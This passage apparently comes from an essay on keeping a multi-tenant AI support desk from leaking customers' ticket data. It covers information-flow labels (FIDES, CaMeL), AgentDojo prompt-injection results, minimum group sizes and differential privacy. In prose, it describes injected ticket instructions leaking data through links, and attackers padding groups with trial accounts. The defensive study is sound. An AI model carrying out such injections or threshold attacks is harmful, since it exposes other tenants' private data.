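The manager loses detail. The paragraph can include a count of 25 payment problems, but not the fact that most of them mention the same bank. A new kind of fault will be counted under "Other" until somebody adds a category. A model could propose categories, but if it reads everyone's raw tickets to do so, the name of a category can leak data. To see the detail, the manager would have to notice that A has an unusual number of payment problems and then open A's tickets in a separate session.

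No model needs to read the tickets to answer questions that code can answer. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that a model write a database query from the user's question, and that ordinary code run the query and draw the chart. Text in the database then can't influence the model, but the model also can't see whether its query answered the question.

The pattern's security comes from its structure. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues analyze the designs of ten such applications but report no attack tests, so a provider would still have to check that its own software enforces the format everywhere.

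### Labels that follow the data

Information-flow control allows free text but keeps a record of whose data went into it. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give each piece of data a label that lists its permitted readers. A text drawn from two sources may go only to readers on both lists:

readers(*x* and *y*) = readers(*x*) ∩ readers(*y*)

Suppose A and the provider's staff can read A's tickets, and C and the staff can read C's. A paragraph based on both customers' tickets may go only to the staff, since only they are on both lists. The software would refuse to send it to C. It would also refuse a request to `help-status.example` that contained any of it, because that server's owner is on neither list. The rule covers both halves of the leak, whether an attacker caused the request or the model made a mistake.

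Labelling data is easier in a shared database than in most offices, because every row is already marked with its tenant. But these labels aren't always enough, because a hotel guest's record can belong to one tenant and their booking to another.

CaMeL, a design from Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich, separates the agent's plan from the data it handles. A model writes a short program before it sees any untrusted text, for instance to fetch C's open tickets, have an isolated model summarise them and display the result. The stranger's complaint can't add a step to that program. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, who call this approach code-then-execute, note that an injection can still change the text that passes through the steps. The summary could therefore contain a false statement or a link, so CaMeL also tracks where each value came from and checks it before use. Garby and colleagues' retry attack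 shows that those checks can slowly leak a secret.

Costa and colleagues at Microsoft built a related system called FIDES. When a tool returns untrusted text, FIDES stores it under a name such as "email 1" and shows the planning model only the name. The planner can pass the text on without reading it. If the next step depends on the contents, the planner queries an isolated model, and the system can limit the answer to yes or no, or to a choice from a list. Before each tool call, ordinary code checks the labels against the rules.

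The team tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks in which attackers plant instructions. With OpenAI's GPT-4o and no rules, an ordinary agent carried out 152 injected tasks. FIDES without its rules carried out 21, so hiding the text helped but wasn't sufficient. With the rules switched on, no attack succeeded against either agent. (AgentDojo's automatic scoring had counted a few successes, which Costa and colleagues reclassified after reading the records.)

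The price was a large share of the ordinary work. These are the percentages of tasks that the agents completed when nobody was attacking them:

| Tasks | Ordinary agent, no rules | Ordinary agent, with rules | FIDES, with rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 |
| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 |

Some of the failures were intended, because many of the banking tasks require the agent to read a file and do what it says, which the rules forbid. Others happened because GPT-4o mixed up the names of stored texts. OpenAI's reasoning model o1 did better, raising the travel result from 41% to 68%. Both models are old, so a current one would probably fail fewer tasks, but it still couldn't complete the ones the rules forbid.

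For leaking links, the most important limitation of FIDES is that its standard form checks the rules only before tool calls. It treats an answer to the user as harmless, so, like Dongol's proof, it doesn't cover images that the chat window loads. Costa and colleagues say developers can instead check every action, including the final answer. The support provider would need to do that and treat each address in an answer as a message to whoever runs the server at that address.

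The guarantee is also weaker than noninterference. FIDES stops the agent from copying A's data into a forbidden request, but an outsider who can see which tools the agent calls might still infer a little about that data. Costa and colleagues accept this to keep the agent useful.

Labels also tend to spread. A model that has read all 80 tickets may write a reply to C that uses only C's tickets, but the software can't easily tell, so it gives the reply the labels of everything in the context and blocks it. *Sightline* (2026) calls the unnecessary labels "label creep" and tries to remove them by estimating which inputs actually influenced an action. In its tests on AgentDojo, it removed more of them than seven competing methods, the best of which removed 38.3% and the others at most 15.7%. No attack got past the rule against untrusted instructions, but a small share of the attack-related inputs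 lost their labels. Estimating influence makes the system more useful, but gives up some of the certainty that labels were meant to provide.

The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) describes two similar designs. NeuroTaint tracks untrusted influence through both models and ordinary code. Agent-Sentry checks whether untrusted sources have influenced the details of a sensitive tool call.

### Minimum group sizes and added noise

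Labels can't help a provider that wants to send all its customers a report on this month's common problems, because the report draws on every customer's tickets and no customer may read them all. To release the report, the provider needs a way to limit what the report reveals about any one customer.

A common rule is to publish a topic only if enough different people or organisations contributed to it. Anthropic applies this rule in Clio, its tool for studying how people use its Claude models. Clio groups similar conversations, has a model describe each group without private details, and drops groups that are too small.

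With a minimum of three tenants, the provider's report would include 25 payment problems and 24 login problems. It would leave out deliveries, which only C reported, and equipment, which C didn't report. The minimum stops a reader from learning about a problem that only one customer has, but it doesn't protect each customer's numbers. If B and C share their counts, they can subtract their combined 11 payment problems from the total and find that A has 14.

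An attacker can also supply the missing members of a group, so a minimum group size is weak protection where accounts are cheap. Suppose someone suspects that the hotel group has trouble with a particular bank. They open two free trial accounts and file a ticket about that bank from each. If the topic appears in the next report, a third tenant must have mentioned it. Sun and Xiao describe a similar attack on caches that share a text only after a secret number of accounts have sent it. The attacker sends the text from enough accounts to pass any threshold.

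Differential privacy replaces the threshold with a mathematical guarantee. It requires the report to contain some randomness, and it compares two collections of tickets, *D* and *D′*, that differ by a single ticket. For every set *S* of possible reports,

P(report on *D* is in *S*) ≤ e^ε × P(report on *D′* is in *S*)

A smaller ε gives stronger protection. If ε is 1, a report that would appear 10% of the time without Maria Lind's ticket can appear at most about 27% of the time with it. This bound holds whatever else the reader knows, so B and C can learn little more about any one ticket by sharing what they know.

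For a count, the usual method is to add random noise proportional to the largest change one ticket can cause. A ticket changes the number of payment problems by at most one. With ε at 1, the noise has a standard deviation of about 1.4, so the report might give 24 or 27 instead of 25, which is still useful.

This calculation assumes that software classifies each ticket alone. If one model call reads all of A's tickets, an instruction in one of them could change how the model classifies all 40, and the noise would have to be 40 times as large. The extra calls in the two-stage design prevent this by classifying each ticket separately. The model that writes the report must also see only the noisy counts, because the guarantee no longer holds once it reads a raw ticket. Google's Urania, which produces reports like Clio's with differential privacy, follows this principle. It selects keywords for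 each group of conversations under the guarantee, and a model writes the description from those keywords.

Noise that hides a single ticket may not hide facts about the tenant as a whole. A's competitors might not care about Maria Lind, but they would like to know that A has many payment problems. Hiding whether A is in the data at all requires enough noise to cover all 40 of its tickets, which means a standard deviation of about 57 at the same ε. That is too much noise for a total of 25 to be useful. A provider with 2,000 tenants of up to 40 tickets each, and 20,000 payment problems between them, could add the same noise and change the total by about 0.3%. The method therefore suits large services much better than a support desk with three customers.

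Publishing repeatedly also weakens the protection. In the worst case the values of ε add up, so weekly reports at ε = 1 reach a total of 52 after a year, which guarantees practically nothing. To avoid this, the provider has to publish less often, add more noise or limit how much each tenant contributes.

Within these limits, the design covers both halves of the leak for the report. An injected instruction can leak little, because any link in the report could carry only noisy counts that the provider has already decided to release. But the report can't replace the staff's own summary, because noise that hides whether Maria Lind's refund exists also keeps the staff from seeing that somebody still has to pay it.
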